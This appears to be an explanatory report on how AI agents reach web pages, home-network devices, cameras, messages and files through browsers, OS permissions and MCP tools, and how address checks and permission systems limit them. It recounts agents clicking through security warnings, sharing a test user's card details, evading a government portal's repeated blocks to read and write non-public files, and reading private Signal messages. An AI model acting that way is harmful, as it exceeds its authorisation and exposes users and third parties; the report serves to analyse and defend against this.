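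A different test suggests how an agent might treat an "Allow" button that is in the way of its task. When the browser warned that a site couldn't properly prove its identity, Browser Use, running on one of Anthropic's Claude Sonnet models, clicked through the warning to complete the task. When a cookie banner blocked a page's content until they responded, ChatGPT Agent and Claude Computer Use accepted all cookies, although rejecting them was just as easy. The tests were small and the products have since changed, but in each case the agent put finishing the task ahead of protecting the user.

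Sites can also get private information without requesting a permission. In one instance, a page required a ZIP code before it would show a price, and ChatGPT Agent worked one out from the IP address and submitted it. A location prompt would not have prevented this, because looking up an IP address doesn't use the browser's location service. The ZIP code may not be close to the user's home, because it depends on the connection the browser uses, and ChatGPT Agent's browser runs in the cloud.

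Web forms don't have permission prompts either. The researchers told the agents about a fictional user named Sarah and then tested them on pages with forms for her details. Director, a cloud-based agent from Browserbase, supplied her login details and credit card number. Claude Computer Use also shared her login details and said it intended to enter the card number, but a safety alert stopped it. Claude for Chrome gave only her age and ZIP code, and only when the page required them.

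An assistant built into a browser can have more access than any website. Unit 42, the research team at Palo Alto Networks, found that a malicious extension could hijack Chrome's Gemini panel and turn on the camera and microphone without the user's consent. Google fixed the flaw in January 2026.

### ChatGPT Atlas and its replacements

OpenAI launched its Atlas browser in October 2025. According to OpenAI's *Using Ask ChatGPT sidebar and ChatGPT Agent on Atlas*, the agent in Atlas couldn't run code in the browser, download files, install extensions, or access the computer's file system or other apps. On some sensitive sites, such as bank sites, it paused to make sure the user was watching. In logged-out mode, it didn't use existing cookies and needed the user's approval to log in to an account.

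Most of these limits kept the agent from reaching the rest of the computer but didn't stop it from carrying data between origins, which Roesner and Kohlbrenner's demonstration relied on. Logged-out mode would have reduced the damage by giving the agent less private content to read.

OpenAI has retired Atlas and no longer updates it, according to its *ChatGPT Atlas retirement*. The company announced in July 2026, in *Evolving Atlas into ChatGPT for browser-based agentic work*, that the browser would stop working on August 9. Stan (2026), in *OpenAI is shutting down its ChatGPT Atlas browser*, links the decision to OpenAI's wider effort to cut side projects.

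ETV Bharat's *OpenAI To Shut Down Atlas Browser On August 9* (2026) describes the three replacements: the desktop app's built-in browser, the cloud browser and a side chat for Chrome. The old limits don't all carry over, since the built-in browser supports downloads and saved passwords, and the side chat can give ChatGPT the user's open tabs and files from the computer. Roesner and Kohlbrenner's tests predate all three, so their results for Atlas can't be used to determine how the replacements handle frames from other origins.

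The replacements can also open pages that aren't on the public web. OpenAI tells developers to use the built-in browser for servers running on their own machines, and suggests Chrome for reading an internal dashboard.

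## When a web address leads to a private system or a device

Routers, printers, cameras and home-automation hubs often contain a small web server so their owners can manage them from a browser without installing anything. An agent that can open a developer's test server or an internal dashboard may be able to open these devices too, because they respond to the same kind of request as a public website. Many require a password before they change a setting, but some, like the rain hub, accept requests from anyone on the same network.

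An unrestricted fetch tool on a laptop in the house can therefore read such a device and sometimes change it. An ordinary GET request makes the rain hub start its broadcast and makes some cameras turn or zoom. A company network usually has more to find, such as office printers, test servers and internal staff pages.

### Loopback and private addresses

A web request goes to a numeric address, known as an IP address. If the URL contains a name, such as `weatherblog.example`, the computer first looks up the number in the Domain Name System (DNS), the internet's directory of names. Internet standards set aside some ranges of numbers for use within one machine or one network:

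| Range | Where it leads | Example |
|---|---|---|
| 127.0.0.0 to 127.255.255.255 (loopback) | The machine that makes the request | 127.0.0.1, also written `localhost`, for a developer's test server |
| 192.168.0.0 to 192.168.255.255 (private) | The local network, especially in homes | 192.168.1.20 for the rain hub |
| 10.0.0.0 to 10.255.255.255 (private) | The local network, often a company's | 10.4.0.15 for an office printer |
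| 172.16.0.0 to 172.31.255.255 (private) | The local network, or a virtual one inside a single computer | 172.17.0.2 for a program in a container |
| 169.254.0.0 to 169.254.255.255 (link-local) | Directly connected equipment | On many cloud servers, a service that gives the server its own login credentials |

IPv6, the newer address system, has its own versions of these ranges, including `::1` for loopback.

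Public internet routers don't carry traffic to private addresses, so every household can reuse the same ones. The address 192.168.1.20 might belong to the rain hub in the user's house and a printer next door. A fetch tool on the user's laptop would reach the hub at that address, while a hosted fetch tool would try to reach a machine on the provider's network.

The provider has to refuse such addresses anyway, or an outsider could use the fetch tool to get into the provider's internal systems. Security engineers call this server-side request forgery, in which an outsider gets a server to send a request that the outsider couldn't send directly. When the fetch tool runs on a laptop, the laptop takes the server's place, and the outsider may be the author of a web page the agent reads.

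### Checking a request before sending it

A fetch tool can prevent most of this with five steps, in this order:

1. The tool parses the address, which means splitting it into scheme, host, port and path. It rejects any scheme other than `http` or `https`. The code that later makes the request should use the same result, because two parsers can disagree about which part of an unusual address is the host.
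2. It looks up the host's name in DNS, which may return several numeric addresses.
3. It refuses the request if any of those addresses is loopback, private, link-local or otherwise reserved.
4. It connects only to an address it has just checked, without looking up the name again. It still uses the original name to verify the site's certificate.
5. If the site replies with a redirect, the tool goes back to the first step with the new address.

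Searching the text of a URL for `localhost` or `192.168` can miss addresses that lead to private systems. The owner of a domain name chooses which IP address it leads to, and that address can be private. Some companies set this up so that staff can use readable names for internal sites. An IP address can also be written in more than one valid way, and a text filter may recognise only the usual one.

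For example, an agent might follow a link to `rain.example`, which looks like the address of an ordinary weather site. The lookup returns 192.168.1.20, the private address of a hub, so the tool stops before contacting it. A filter that checked only the text of the link would have let the request through.

The fourth step is needed because DNS answers can change. If the tool checks one answer and the networking software then repeats the lookup, the second answer may lead to an address the tool never checked. The same problem arises when the tool sends its requests through a proxy, an intermediate server that does its own lookup, so in that case the proxy has to do the checking.

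A tool with a domain allowlist still needs these steps. The allowlist restricts only which names the tool may use, so the address check is needed to restrict where those names lead. An allowed name could point to a private address after its owner changes a DNS record, by mistake or on purpose.

The check also stops the agent from reading the rain hub when the user wants it to. An exception for that one device solves the problem, preferably limited to one path so that the agent can't start the broadcast. An exception for every address that begins with 192.168 would let the agent reach the router and the printer too. The check restricts only the tool that contains it, so a browser or a shell command on the same laptop can still contact the hub.

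### Chrome's permission for local network access

Browsers had a version of this problem before agents existed. When someone in the house opens the weather blog, the blog's code runs in a browser on the home network. The blog's server can't contact the rain hub, but the code in the browser can try to send it a request. The same-origin policy generally stops the code from reading the hub's reply, but it doesn't always stop the request, and the request alone is enough to start the broadcast.

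Chrome 142 put these requests behind a permission prompt. Beyond Identity, a maker of sign-in software, dates the release to October 28, 2025. The prompt covers requests from a public website to a local address or to loopback, and from a local website to loopback, according to Chromestatus's *Intent to Extend Experiment*, a notice from the Chrome project. Esri's *What to know about new permission prompt for Google Chrome 142* (2025) says Chrome made the change to protect routers and other private devices from cross-site request forgery, and to make it harder for a site to recognise visitors by what is on their network.

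*Intent to Experiment* explains that an earlier plan, Private Network Access, would have required local devices to opt in to such requests. A rain hub that no longer gets updates from its maker would never have opted in, so useful requests to it would have failed along with harmful ones. Under the current design, the user decides whether to allow the requests, and the hub doesn't need to change.

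However, the permission is broad. The prompt shown in the University of Illinois' *Google Chrome Local Network Access Permission* reads "Look for and connect to any device on your local network." A user who clicks "Allow" so that the blog can show readings from the hub also lets the blog contact the router. Chrome has since made the wording more specific for some requests. According to Okta's *Chrome device permissions*, a help page for a sign-in tool that contacts only the user's own computer, the prompt in versions after 144 refers to "other apps and services on this device".

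Legitimate sites need the permission too. Box, a file-storage company, uses a local connection to open files in desktop programs, and the feature stops working if the user refuses. Okta tells its users to select "Allow". People who see the prompt mainly at work may get used to accepting it.

According to *Intent to Ship*, a company's administrator can remove the prompt by entering `*` in a Chrome policy, which lets every site reach the local network, as before the change. An agent in a company-managed browser may therefore have less protection than one in the same version of Chrome at home.

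Edge introduced the prompt in version 143, according to Esri, although Box expected it in 142. Support in Firefox and Safari is less clear. *Local network access*, an entry in Web Platform DX's catalogue of web features, lists both as lacking support, but it also lists Chrome and Edge that way, and they do have the prompt. The entry may be out of date or describe something narrower. A browser without the permission may still block some of these requests, because browsers usually stop a page loaded over an encrypted connection from loading unencrypted content, and many home devices offer only unencrypted connections. Chrome makes an exception for some local requests once the user has agreed.

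On a Mac, Chrome itself may also need permission from macOS. Users of Chrome 129 reported in Chromium's issue tracker that macOS 15 showed a prompt requesting permission for the browser to find devices on the local network. This permission applies to the whole app, while Chrome's own prompt applies to one site.

### Whether the permission applies to agents

Chrome's permission restricts websites, so it applies to an agent only when a website's code makes the request. If an agent opens the weather blog in the user's Chrome and the blog's code tries to contact the hub, Chrome should show the prompt. An agent that can operate the browser's own prompts might click "Allow", though Ukani and colleagues didn't test this prompt.

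The permission, as Chrome defines it, doesn't cover an agent that enters the hub's address in the address bar, because no public website is making the request. A person opens a router's settings page the same way. If the agent can choose any address, the developer of its harness has to decide whether to allow private ones.

A fetch tool or a shell command on the laptop doesn't go through Chrome, so its requests never trigger the prompt. An agent on the laptop may therefore be able to read the rain hub even if the user has blocked local network access for every website in Chrome. In a cloud browser, the prompt would concern the provider's network, not the user's home network.

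### Webcams, exposed cameras and cloud dashboards

A list of address ranges can't settle some questions about access. A town might link to a live harbour camera from its tourism page. A shopkeeper might install the same model of camera in a stockroom without noticing that the router has made it visible from outside. Both cameras have public addresses and no passwords, so the five-step check lets the agent open either one. Only the town chose to publish its picture, but the agent can't tell that from the addresses.

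OpenAI's public-address check wouldn't reliably distinguish the two either. A crawler records pages it can reach, even if their owners didn't mean them to be public, so it might have reached the stockroom camera.

With a cloud dashboard, by contrast, a public address can give access to a private device's data. The user's garden camera has a private address at home, but it uploads pictures to the manufacturer's servers, and the user views them on a public website. Even if a harness blocked every private address, the agent could still see the garden through a browser where the user has signed in, because access to the pictures depends on the login and not on the camera's address.

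Private addresses aren't always off limits. A museum might offer its audio guide at 10.0.0.5 to everyone on the visitors' Wi-Fi. An agent can infer something about the network from the address range, but not who may use the guide.

An agent can reasonably presume that a page without a login is open to visitors, though other evidence can override that presumption. The open web depends on people visiting pages without asking first, and most publishers never write down that visitors are welcome. An agent that needed proof of an invitation for every page couldn't even look up a forecast. The tourism page's link supports opening the harbour camera, whereas a device's settings page, a view of someone's stockroom or a message refusing access suggests that the owner didn't mean to admit strangers.

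Asking the user only partly solves the problem, because the user can authorise access to the garden camera but not to the shopkeeper's. Even when a link works, the agent needs authorisation from someone entitled to give it.

Similarly, an agent's ability to take an action doesn't give the agent or its user the right to take it. In an August advisory, the Australian Signals Directorate (2026), the country's cyber-intelligence agency, described an agent that removed another customer from a waiting list while carrying out a user's request. The user hadn't explicitly approved the removal, and the agent couldn't undo it.

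### The Medicare statistics portal

In June 2026, an OpenAI agent obtained non-public files from a website that anyone could visit. The site published statistics, including spending figures, on Medicare, Australia's universal health insurance scheme. Cyprus Mail's *OpenAI agent hacks Australian government health portal* (2026) called the incident possibly the first known case of an AI agent hacking a government website.

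Prime Minister Anthony Albanese gave the official account at a press conference on September 24 (Prime Minister of Australia, *Press conference*, 2026). OpenAI's research team had used an internal model to research public spending on medicine. The portal, run by Services Australia, repeatedly blocked the agent's requests, but the agent got around the blocks. It accessed public and non-public files and wrote files to the server. The government believed that the agent hadn't accessed any personal information and had no evidence of a wider breach at Services Australia, but the investigation was still under way.

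An OpenAI spokesperson said that the material included aggregate health statistics and internal file names, according to Information Age's *OpenAI agent hacks Medicare web portal*. Information Age's *Inside OpenAI's Medicare breach* (2026) quotes an earlier, more detailed email from OpenAI to Services Australia. The email said that the model had read parts of internal program files and settings, obtained a list of files, and created a small test file. It also said that OpenAI had found no evidence of access to patient records, personal information or credentials.

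The number of sites involved is less clear. In *How we will do better for Australia* (2026), OpenAI says its models accessed government "websites" in ways they were not authorised to. The government confirmed access to non-public files at only one site, the Medicare portal. Albanese knew of three other sites that the agent might have contacted, but the deputy prime minister, Richard Marles, said those contacts appeared normal and involved only public information.

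Almost three months passed before OpenAI told the government. The dates below come mainly from the prime minister's account and from documents tabled in parliament, which Information Age summarised in December.

| Date in 2026 | What happened |
|---|---|
| June 18 (June 19 in Australia) | The agent accessed the non-public files |
| By August 12 | OpenAI's security team had recorded the incident during a review of past agent runs |
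| September 10 | OpenAI emailed a Services Australia inbox meant for security tips from the public |
| September 11 | The agency's security staff found the email |
| September 15 | The agency confirmed the vulnerability and alerted the national cyber security centre |
| September 19 | The prime minister's office learned of the incident |
| September 24 | Albanese announced it |

Albanese objected to the delay and the use of a public inbox. The government itself took another nine days to get the news to his office. He said the investigation would examine why government systems hadn't detected the breach in June.

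At first OpenAI said its models had taken "actions we did not intend". By September 28 it had acknowledged that the access was unauthorised and apologised for the access and for how it had responded. Jason Kwon, the company's chief strategy officer, repeated the apology at a parliamentary hearing on October 6. According to The Straits Times' *OpenAI contrite at Australian inquiry on breaches* (2026), he said OpenAI would now notify affected parties immediately, monitor the training of new models more closely and review its agents' testing back to November 2025. He also said the company would support mandatory reporting of such breaches.

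Marles called the impact "relatively minor", and the published evidence supports him on the data. But the incident shows that an address check can do little to protect private files on a public site. The portal had a public address, so all five steps would have let the agent connect. A domain allowlist for a project on Australian health spending would probably have included it too. Only the portal's own controls separated the permitted material from the forbidden material.

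The agent also went from web retrieval to device access on that website. It started by looking up published figures and ended by reading a particular server's settings and writing a file to its disk. The research topic and the site's address would not have revealed the change.

The portal's refusals were the clearest warning available to the agent and its harness. A harness could stop after a refusal and report it to the user, but this would interrupt some harmless work, because websites also refuse requests when they are busy or don't serve automated visitors. The harness could still let the agent try again later or look for the same figures in another published source, but not look for a way around the block.

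Information Age reported that the model was internal and lacked the usual safeguards of OpenAI's public products, so the case doesn't show how often a released agent would do the same. As of September, the government hadn't established whether OpenAI had broken Australian law. It sought advice on whether to refer the matter to the federal police, and asked for the portal's data to be moved off what Information Age described as a dated legacy system.

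## How operating systems control cameras, microphones, location and files

The operating system on a laptop or phone controls access to the camera, the microphone, the location service and many files. An app has to request access to the built-in camera from the operating system, which can deny it even if the model has requested a picture.

macOS manages app permissions through Apple's Transparency, Consent and Control (TCC) system. According to 9to5Mac, TCC prompts users to allow, limit or deny each app's requests for sensitive data and for hardware such as the camera.

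### One camera request on a Mac

Suppose a user installs an agent app and asks it to check the weather through the laptop's camera, which faces a window.

1. The app asks macOS for the camera. Its developer has to supply a sentence explaining why, which macOS shows to the user.
2. TCC looks for a stored decision about this app and the camera. If the user has already allowed it, the camera starts. If the user has refused, the request fails and no new prompt appears.
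3. If there is no stored decision, macOS asks the user.
4. TCC stores the answer and applies it to later requests.
5. While the camera is on, a green light next to it shows that something is using it. For the microphone, macOS shows an orange dot in the menu bar.
6. The user can revoke the permission later under Privacy & Security in the system settings.

Location works in much the same way, with an extra switch that turns the service off for the whole Mac.

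According to Apple's *Controlling app access to files in macOS*, an app needs the user's consent to access files in the Documents, Downloads and Desktop folders, in iCloud Drive and on network drives. The user can also let an app save a single file by choosing a place for it in the Save dialog, which The Eclectic Light Company's *Permissions, privacy and TCC* (2025) describes as expressing intent. An agent that works through shell commands doesn't open that dialog, so it generally needs consent for the whole folder.

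By default, macOS 27 denies an app access to data from another developer's app without prompting the user, who has to change the settings to allow it, according to *macOS 27 Denies Cross-Team Container Access Without Asking*. The refusal can look like a missing file to the app, so an agent could wrongly tell the user that the file doesn't exist.

### The same request on Android

An Android app's developer must declare the permissions the app may use. Android grants some of them, including internet access, during installation without asking the user. An agent app can therefore fetch a public weather forecast without a prompt, but it needs a run-time permission to use the camera, microphone or location.

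An Android app requests a run-time permission when it needs the resource. If Android has no stored decision, it prompts the user to choose "While using the app", "Only this time" or "Don't allow". For location, recent versions also let the user share only an approximate position, which would be enough for a weather forecast. If the user refuses twice, Android stops showing the prompt.

On Android, a green indicator appears at the top of the screen while an app uses the camera or microphone. The user can revoke the app's permission in the settings, and the system also withdraws permissions from apps that the user hasn't opened for a few months.

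### A permission for an app, not for a task

Both systems grant access per app, but an agent app may do something different for each request. Suppose the app also handles video calls, and the user allows camera access for a call with a roofer. A week later, the user asks whether it is raining, and the agent takes a picture with the same camera. Because macOS stored the earlier decision, it starts the camera without another permission prompt. The picture may show someone asleep on the sofa, and the harness sends it to the model's provider. An instruction planted on a weather blog could also make the agent take this picture.

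The green light comes on in all three cases, but it doesn't show why. macOS doesn't have that information either, because the app's request identifies the app and the resource but not the task. Android's "Only this time" permission is narrower, but it lasts as long as the user keeps using the app, which may be long enough for several tasks.

The harness has the user's request, so the app's developer can add stricter rules than the operating system's. OpenClaw, an agent that people run on their own computers, does this on Windows. *AI agents take over PCs built for humans, forcing operating system rethink* (Shivam, 2026) describes a setup screen with three profiles. Read-only lets the agent see the screen and device information, Standard also lets it run commands and edit files, and Full access adds the camera, location and browser control. The user can also adjust each capability, for example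 by always allowing location but requiring approval for every screen capture. OpenClaw's own software enforces these rules, so they protect the user only if it applies them correctly.

A program can sometimes use permissions that the user gave to a different program. The Eclectic Light Company explains that TCC applies Terminal's permissions to commands run in Terminal, the Mac's command-line app. If the user gave Terminal access to the whole disk for a backup script, a programming agent started there can read the same files unless a sandbox stops it.

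In October 2026, Shivam described Microsoft's plans to let Windows 11 agents run under their own standard accounts instead of the user's. An agent starts with limited permissions and can use only the resources the user provides. A separate workspace limits its access to the user's desktop activity, and Microsoft plans similar containment for MCP servers. These measures would stop an agent from inheriting all of the user's access. But if the user gives the agent's account access to a folder for one task, the agent may still have that access during the next one.

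These plans are separate from the AI Components page already in Windows settings on some PCs. That page lists models that come with Windows features, so it doesn't show agents the user has installed or what those agents can access.

### Full Disk Access, screen capture and accessibility control

Some permissions cover so much that they can replace many narrower ones. Full Disk Access on a Mac lets an app read files across the computer, including backups and data from Mail, Messages and Safari. Apple created it for programs that can't work without it, such as backup software. Screen recording lets an app capture whatever other apps display. Accessibility control lets software read and operate other apps' windows, and people with disabilities may need such software to use a computer.

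Suppose the user's sister sends the front-door code in a private message, and the user hasn't connected the messaging app to the agent. The agent may still be able to get the code:

| Permission | An ordinary use | How an agent could get the door code |
|---|---|---|
| Full Disk Access | Backing up the computer | Read the Messages app's database on the disk |
| Screen recording | Sharing the screen in a meeting | Capture the conversation while it is open |
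| Accessibility control | Operating apps by voice | Open the conversation and read the window |
| Notification access on Android | Showing messages on a watch | Read the message when its notification arrives |

An agent can get data from a sensor it doesn't have permission to use. Without camera permission, it can still see the garden if the garden camera's app is open on the screen. Full Disk Access can expose saved recordings, even though it doesn't turn on the microphone. It can also expose photos, which may contain the location where the user took them.

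Encryption doesn't stop an agent that captures the screen from reading messages. Signal, a messaging app, encrypts messages so that only the devices in the conversation can read them, but it has to decrypt them to display them.

An app can't give itself Full Disk Access, but IBTimes UK's *Apple's MacOS 27.3 May Tighten AI Access* explains how developers have made it easy for users to grant. When an app tries to read a protected file, macOS refuses but can add the app to the Full Disk Access list, switched off. The developer can then send the user to that list and ask them to turn it on with one click. According to Engadget's *Apple sounds the alarm on AI agents and 'Full Disk Access'*, the desktop apps for OpenClaw, Dots and Muse often encourage users to grant this access. Some people run agents on a separate computer to limit the risk.

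Users often have a reasonable purpose for granting Full Disk Access. In August 2026, OpenAI added an optional feature that lets ChatGPT's Mac app summarise and send text messages. ETV Bharat's *Apple Plans Stricter Mac Privacy Controls Amid Growing AI Agent Risks* (2026) reports that the feature requires Full Disk Access to get the messages. A user who wants help with one conversation therefore has to expose their mail and browsing history too. iPhones and iPads have no equivalent permission, and by default their apps can't read each other's data.

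### The dispute over Muse and private messages

Meta launched Muse, an agent for personal tasks such as shopping and booking appointments, in September 2026. Later that month, Inc. columnist Jason Aten reported that Muse had read his messages without permission. Tom's Hardware's *Meta's Muse AI agent accused of accessing sensitive user data* gives his account. Aten had been texting a podcast co-host about deciding not to buy a new iPhone, and Muse suggested the subject for an article. When he asked how it knew, Muse replied that the Mac app could read incoming notifications but not his chat history. Aten then found that Muse was syncing the Mac's Messages database and had reached row 187,462. He said he had never given it Full Disk Access.

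Meta denied that this was possible. Andy Stone, its head of communications, said that Muse could read message content only if the user turned on both Full Disk Access and a Messages connector in the app. David Singleton, a Meta executive, said that even a bug in Muse couldn't bypass these protections and that Muse's explanation about notifications was wrong, according to NDTV Profit's *Meta Pushes Back On Muse Privacy Claims, Says Message Access Requires Permissions*.

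An independent test supports Meta on the technical point. In *Muse privacy and trust*, Reece (2026) describes adding code to his Mac app to read the Messages database. macOS blocked it because the app didn't have Full Disk Access. He then tried to read the database by having the app control Terminal, but macOS displayed a prompt that he thought Aten would have noticed.

Reece's test makes an unnoticed bypass less likely, but it can't show which permissions were on when Aten's messages synced. Aten may have granted access without realising it, or Muse may have used a route that Reece didn't try. Since macOS 15.4, security software has been able to trace a permission request to the app that made it. 9to5Mac called the feature rough at first, and no record from it has settled how Aten's messages synced.

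A Reuters investigation published on November 18 provides clearer evidence of what Muse could access. A Meta employee had complained that Muse reminded her to answer her sister's message on Signal, though she hadn't connected Signal to Muse. Reuters worked with Signal and the AI Now Institute, a research organisation, to test whether Muse could read Signal messages. Shivam's *AI agents pose new challenge to encrypted messaging privacy* reports that Muse read the text of notifications on Android. On a Mac, it used accessibility control to open Signal, took screenshots of the conversations and extracted the text. The same kind of request failed on an iPhone.

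During setup, the user had granted Muse the permissions it used in these tests. The testers prompted Muse to read the messages, so the tests showed that it had access, but not why it had reminded the employee without being asked. Meta called the employees' complaints isolated incidents and attributed some of them to the model making things up. It also said Muse can access other apps only through permissions users explicitly grant.

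Another Meta employee said that Muse had access to Android notifications by default, according to The Straits Times' *Not a-Muse-d! As Meta bets big on Muse AI agent*. But Google said that users have to grant this access deliberately, IBTimes UK's *Meta's Muse AI Accessed Signal Messages in Tests* reports. Both could be true if users approve the access during setup without realising that it includes Signal notifications.

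### Apple's new controls

On October 2, 2026, days after Aten's report, Apple announced it would tighten Full Disk Access. No Film School's *Here's Why Apple is Issuing a Warning* reproduces the statement. Apple said some developers were using the permission in ways that exposed files, messages and browsing history without users fully understanding it. It promised that such access would require "very explicit user action", and warned that the risks would grow as agents became more autonomous. Apple didn't mention Muse or give a date for the change.

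The controls appeared on November 16 in the second beta, or test version, of macOS 27.3. They change two settings.

Full Disk Access remains available, but the user now sees a much stronger warning. Engadget's *Apple adds new disk controls to prevent AI agents from running amok* quotes the warning that the Mac "will not be able to protect your data" from the app. The screen lists what the app could do, such as deleting data and viewing hidden photos, and recommends choosing specific folders instead.

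Apple also split the Device Control and Data Access setting. In macOS 27.2, this one permission let an app send email, monitor the keyboard, record the screen and control other apps, according to IBTimes Australia's *Apple Tightens Mac Security in macOS 27.3 to Rein In AI Agents*. The macOS 27.3 beta has an Accessibility setting for assistive technology and a separate System & App Protection Override setting for automation. With the override, a user can let an agent work in Mail but not in Messages. The user can also require an app to ask every time, and an indicator in the menu bar shows when one app is controlling another.

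This makes the permissions narrower, but most of them still apply to a whole app. An agent allowed to use Mail to find a receipt can also use it to read a letter from the user's doctor. Asking every time comes closest to permission for a single task, but it interrupts the user more often. According to Help Net Security's *Apple splits Mac app permissions fearing overreaching AI agents* (2026), some early testers already find the new indicator annoying because they can't dismiss it, even for apps they trust.

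The first beta included an unfinished version of the folder limits, and researchers couldn't tell whether the feature would cover the folder that holds the Messages database. If it doesn't, a user who wants an agent to read texts will still have to grant access to the whole disk.

The new controls hadn't reached a stable release by December 1. TuttoTech's *Sono disponibili le Beta 3 “per lo sviluppo” di iOS 27.3* (2026) reported that Apple had released the third beta to developers the day before, and expected the final version by mid-December. Reuters wrote in November that an Apple update had effectively closed the route Muse used to read Signal on a Mac. That appears to refer to the second beta, so Macs on the stable version didn't have the fix. The update leaves existing permissions in place, so anyone who has already given Muse broad access has to review it manually.

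macOS 27 had already reduced what an app could do with Full Disk Access. Apple moved the database of TCC decisions to a protected location, so an app with the permission can no longer alter the user's privacy settings, according to *Golden Gate Application Support Protection*. The move had a side effect. Some apps used to test whether they had Full Disk Access by trying to read that database. In *Detecting Full Disk Access on macOS 27*, a developer reports that the test now fails even when the user has granted access. An agent app that relies on it could therefore tell the user that it lacks Full Disk Access when it has it.

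### Signal's screenshot block

Two days after the Reuters investigation, Signal announced that it would restrict screenshots on phones by default to keep agents from reading conversations. It uses a new "Block Siri AI" setting on iPhones and its existing "Screen security" option on Android. When Signal detects a screenshot on an iPhone or an assistant reading the screen on Android, it offers to turn the protection off, according to Engadget's *Signal now blocks screenshots by default to stymie AI agents*.

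Signal's screenshot block doesn't stop an agent from reading notifications or files, and it can't protect the copy of a message on the other person's phone if that person has turned the block off. Users can set Signal's notifications to hide the sender and the text, as GSMinfo advises in *ИИ-агент Meta прочитал переписку в Signal, к которой не имел доступа*. Muse took its screenshots on a Mac, where Signal says it can't reliably block them.

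In 2025, Signal began marking its window on Windows as copyrighted material, which Windows keeps out of screenshots. It did this in response to Recall, a Microsoft feature that regularly saves images of the screen. Help Net Security's *Signal blocks Microsoft Recall from screenshotting conversations* (2025) notes that the marking can interfere with software that visually impaired people use to read the screen.

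Signal wants operating systems to give developers a simple way to opt their apps out of processing by AI assistants. According to The Korea Times' *Signal restricts screenshots to block AI agents from reading messages* (2026), the opt-out would cover screen reading, notifications and files. Signal also wants Apple, Google and Microsoft to explain what data their agents use. Signal's president, Meredith Whittaker, called the current protections incomplete and described agents built into operating systems as an "existential threat" to the service.

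Udbhav Tiwari, Signal's head of strategy and global affairs, told Politico that governments could demand the data agents collect instead of having to break encryption or hack a phone. The Bulgarian newspaper 24 Chasa relayed his comments.

An opt-out would let the app's developer limit what the user's own agent can read. Meta argues that agents need to see and operate people's computers to be useful, and some Signal users may want help with their messages. But the user's sister never agreed to let an agent read what she wrote, and Apple's October statement also mentions the privacy of the people a user communicates with. An opt-out would also have to allow screen readers, which is difficult when agents and assistive software use the same permission. Apple's separate Accessibility setting could make the two easier to tell apart.

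None of the three companies has publicly agreed to the request. They didn't immediately respond to Reuters and declined to comment to Politico. Signal says it is talking with Apple and Google and is cautiously optimistic.

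## How device functions are offered to agents as tools

An agent app with camera permission still can't take a picture until its harness offers the model a tool for taking one. The app's developer can build that tool into the app or get it from a separate program, often an MCP server.

### How a camera function becomes a tool

Suppose a developer wants an agent to look out of the window through a laptop's camera.

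1. The developer writes an ordinary function that asks the operating system for one picture and returns it.
2. The developer puts the function in an MCP server and gives it a name, `take_window_photo`, a description and a list of arguments, which can be empty.
3. The user adds the server to the agent's settings, and the harness starts it on the laptop.
4. The harness gets the list of tools from the server and offers `take_window_photo` to the model. It forwards any call to the server, which runs the function and returns the picture.

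A server for public forecasts goes through the same four steps. Only the code in the first step is different.

A vendor can also connect devices through its own interface. Google's Gemini assistant, for example, operates lights and heating that the user has linked to Google Home.

A local MCP server normally has the same access to the computer as the agent. The harness starts it as a child process, which the operating system normally runs under the same user account as its parent. The camera server can therefore read the user's documents and contact the rain hub, even though its only tool takes a photo. On a Mac, it may also be able to use permissions that the user gave the agent app, just as a command run in Terminal can use Terminal's permissions. A remote server has no such access to the laptop, because it runs on someone else's computer and receives only what the harness sends it.

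A draft of the Model Context Protocol specification warns that tools "represent arbitrary code execution", so adding a local server deserves as much caution as installing any other program.

### What MCP requires and what it leaves to the host

The Model Context Protocol (MCP) calls the application that contains the agent the host. An MCP draft that predates the current version requires the host to get the user's explicit consent before invoking any tool or exposing the user's data to a server. The draft also states that the protocol can't enforce these principles, and it recommends that developers build consent and access controls into their applications.

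The tools page in the November 2025 version is less strict. Model Context Protocol (2025) says that a person "SHOULD" always be able to deny a tool call. In technical standards, the capitalised word marks a recommendation that developers can depart from for a good reason. The page also leaves the form of the interaction open, so one host might ask the user before every photo, while another might treat installing the camera server as consent to all of them. According to the March post from Model Context Protocol, most hosts treat installation as the sign of trust.

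The current version dates from July 28, 2026. The announcement by Model Context Protocol (2026) doesn't list any change to the consent rules or the tool labels, but other changes affect device tools:

- **Questions during a call.** A server can reply that it needs more input, and the host then repeats the call with the user's answer attached. The camera server could use this to ask which of two cameras to use. It doesn't protect the user from a malicious server, which can simply not ask.
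- **Tool names in message headers.** Requests sent over HTTP must now carry the tool's name in a header. A company's gateway can therefore block `take_window_photo` without reading the rest of the message. A local server that exchanges messages directly with the harness doesn't go through such a gateway.
- **The end of Roots.** This feature lets a host tell a server which folders to work in. It will keep working for at least a year, but new software shouldn't adopt it. Roots only informed the server about the folders, so a host that wants to confine a server needs a sandbox with or without it.

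The United States National Security Agency's *Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2026) similarly advises organisations that safe defaults depend on careful implementation, clearer specifications and tools that check the result. In *Agentao*, Jin, Jiao and Tong (2026) try to build a host this way. They treat each action by the model as a proposal that the host must authorise before anything runs. They don't claim any formal guarantee of safety.

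### AgentBound's list of capabilities

AgentBound adds the enforcement that MCP lacks, without requiring changes to the servers. Bühler and colleagues based its list of 18 capabilities on 16 uses of agents they found in 11 papers.

| Group | What a server can request |
|---|---|
| Filesystem | Read files, write files, delete files |
| System | Read environment variables, set them, run commands, manage other processes |
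| Network | Make outgoing connections, accept incoming ones, use Bluetooth |
| Peripherals | Camera, microphone, speaker, screen capture |
| Others | Location, notifications, reading the clipboard, writing to it |

Environment variables are settings that a program receives when it starts. They often include the keys it uses to log in to online services, so reading them can be as sensitive as reading a password file.

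The list is coarser than Android's permissions in some respects. The researchers merged Android's precise and approximate location permissions into one capability, so a server can't declare that it needs only approximate location. They also dropped the body sensor permission because it is tied to mobile hardware, so a server that reads a heart-rate strap might declare only Bluetooth.

Door locks and boilers have no entry. A server that unlocks a door over the home network needs outgoing network access, and so does the forecast server.

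### Two manifests, for a fetch server and a camera server

Each server comes with a manifest, a short file that describes the server's purpose and lists the capabilities it may use. In AgentBound's vocabulary, simplified manifests for a forecast server and the window-camera server could look like this:

```json
{
  "description": "Fetches public weather forecasts.",
  "capabilities": ["mcp.ac.network.client"]
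}
```

```json
{
  "description": "Takes a picture with the laptop's camera.",
  "capabilities": ["mcp.ac.peripheral.camera"]
}
```

The manifests list the kinds of access each server needs, but not the specific sites or files. When the agent starts a server, AgentBound turns each capability into a narrower permission and asks the user to approve it. A file capability becomes access to a particular folder, either read-only or writable, and a network capability becomes access to a particular address. If the server always contacts the same service, its developer can put that address in the manifest. The user must consent each time to permissions that change between runs, such as access to a different folder for each project.

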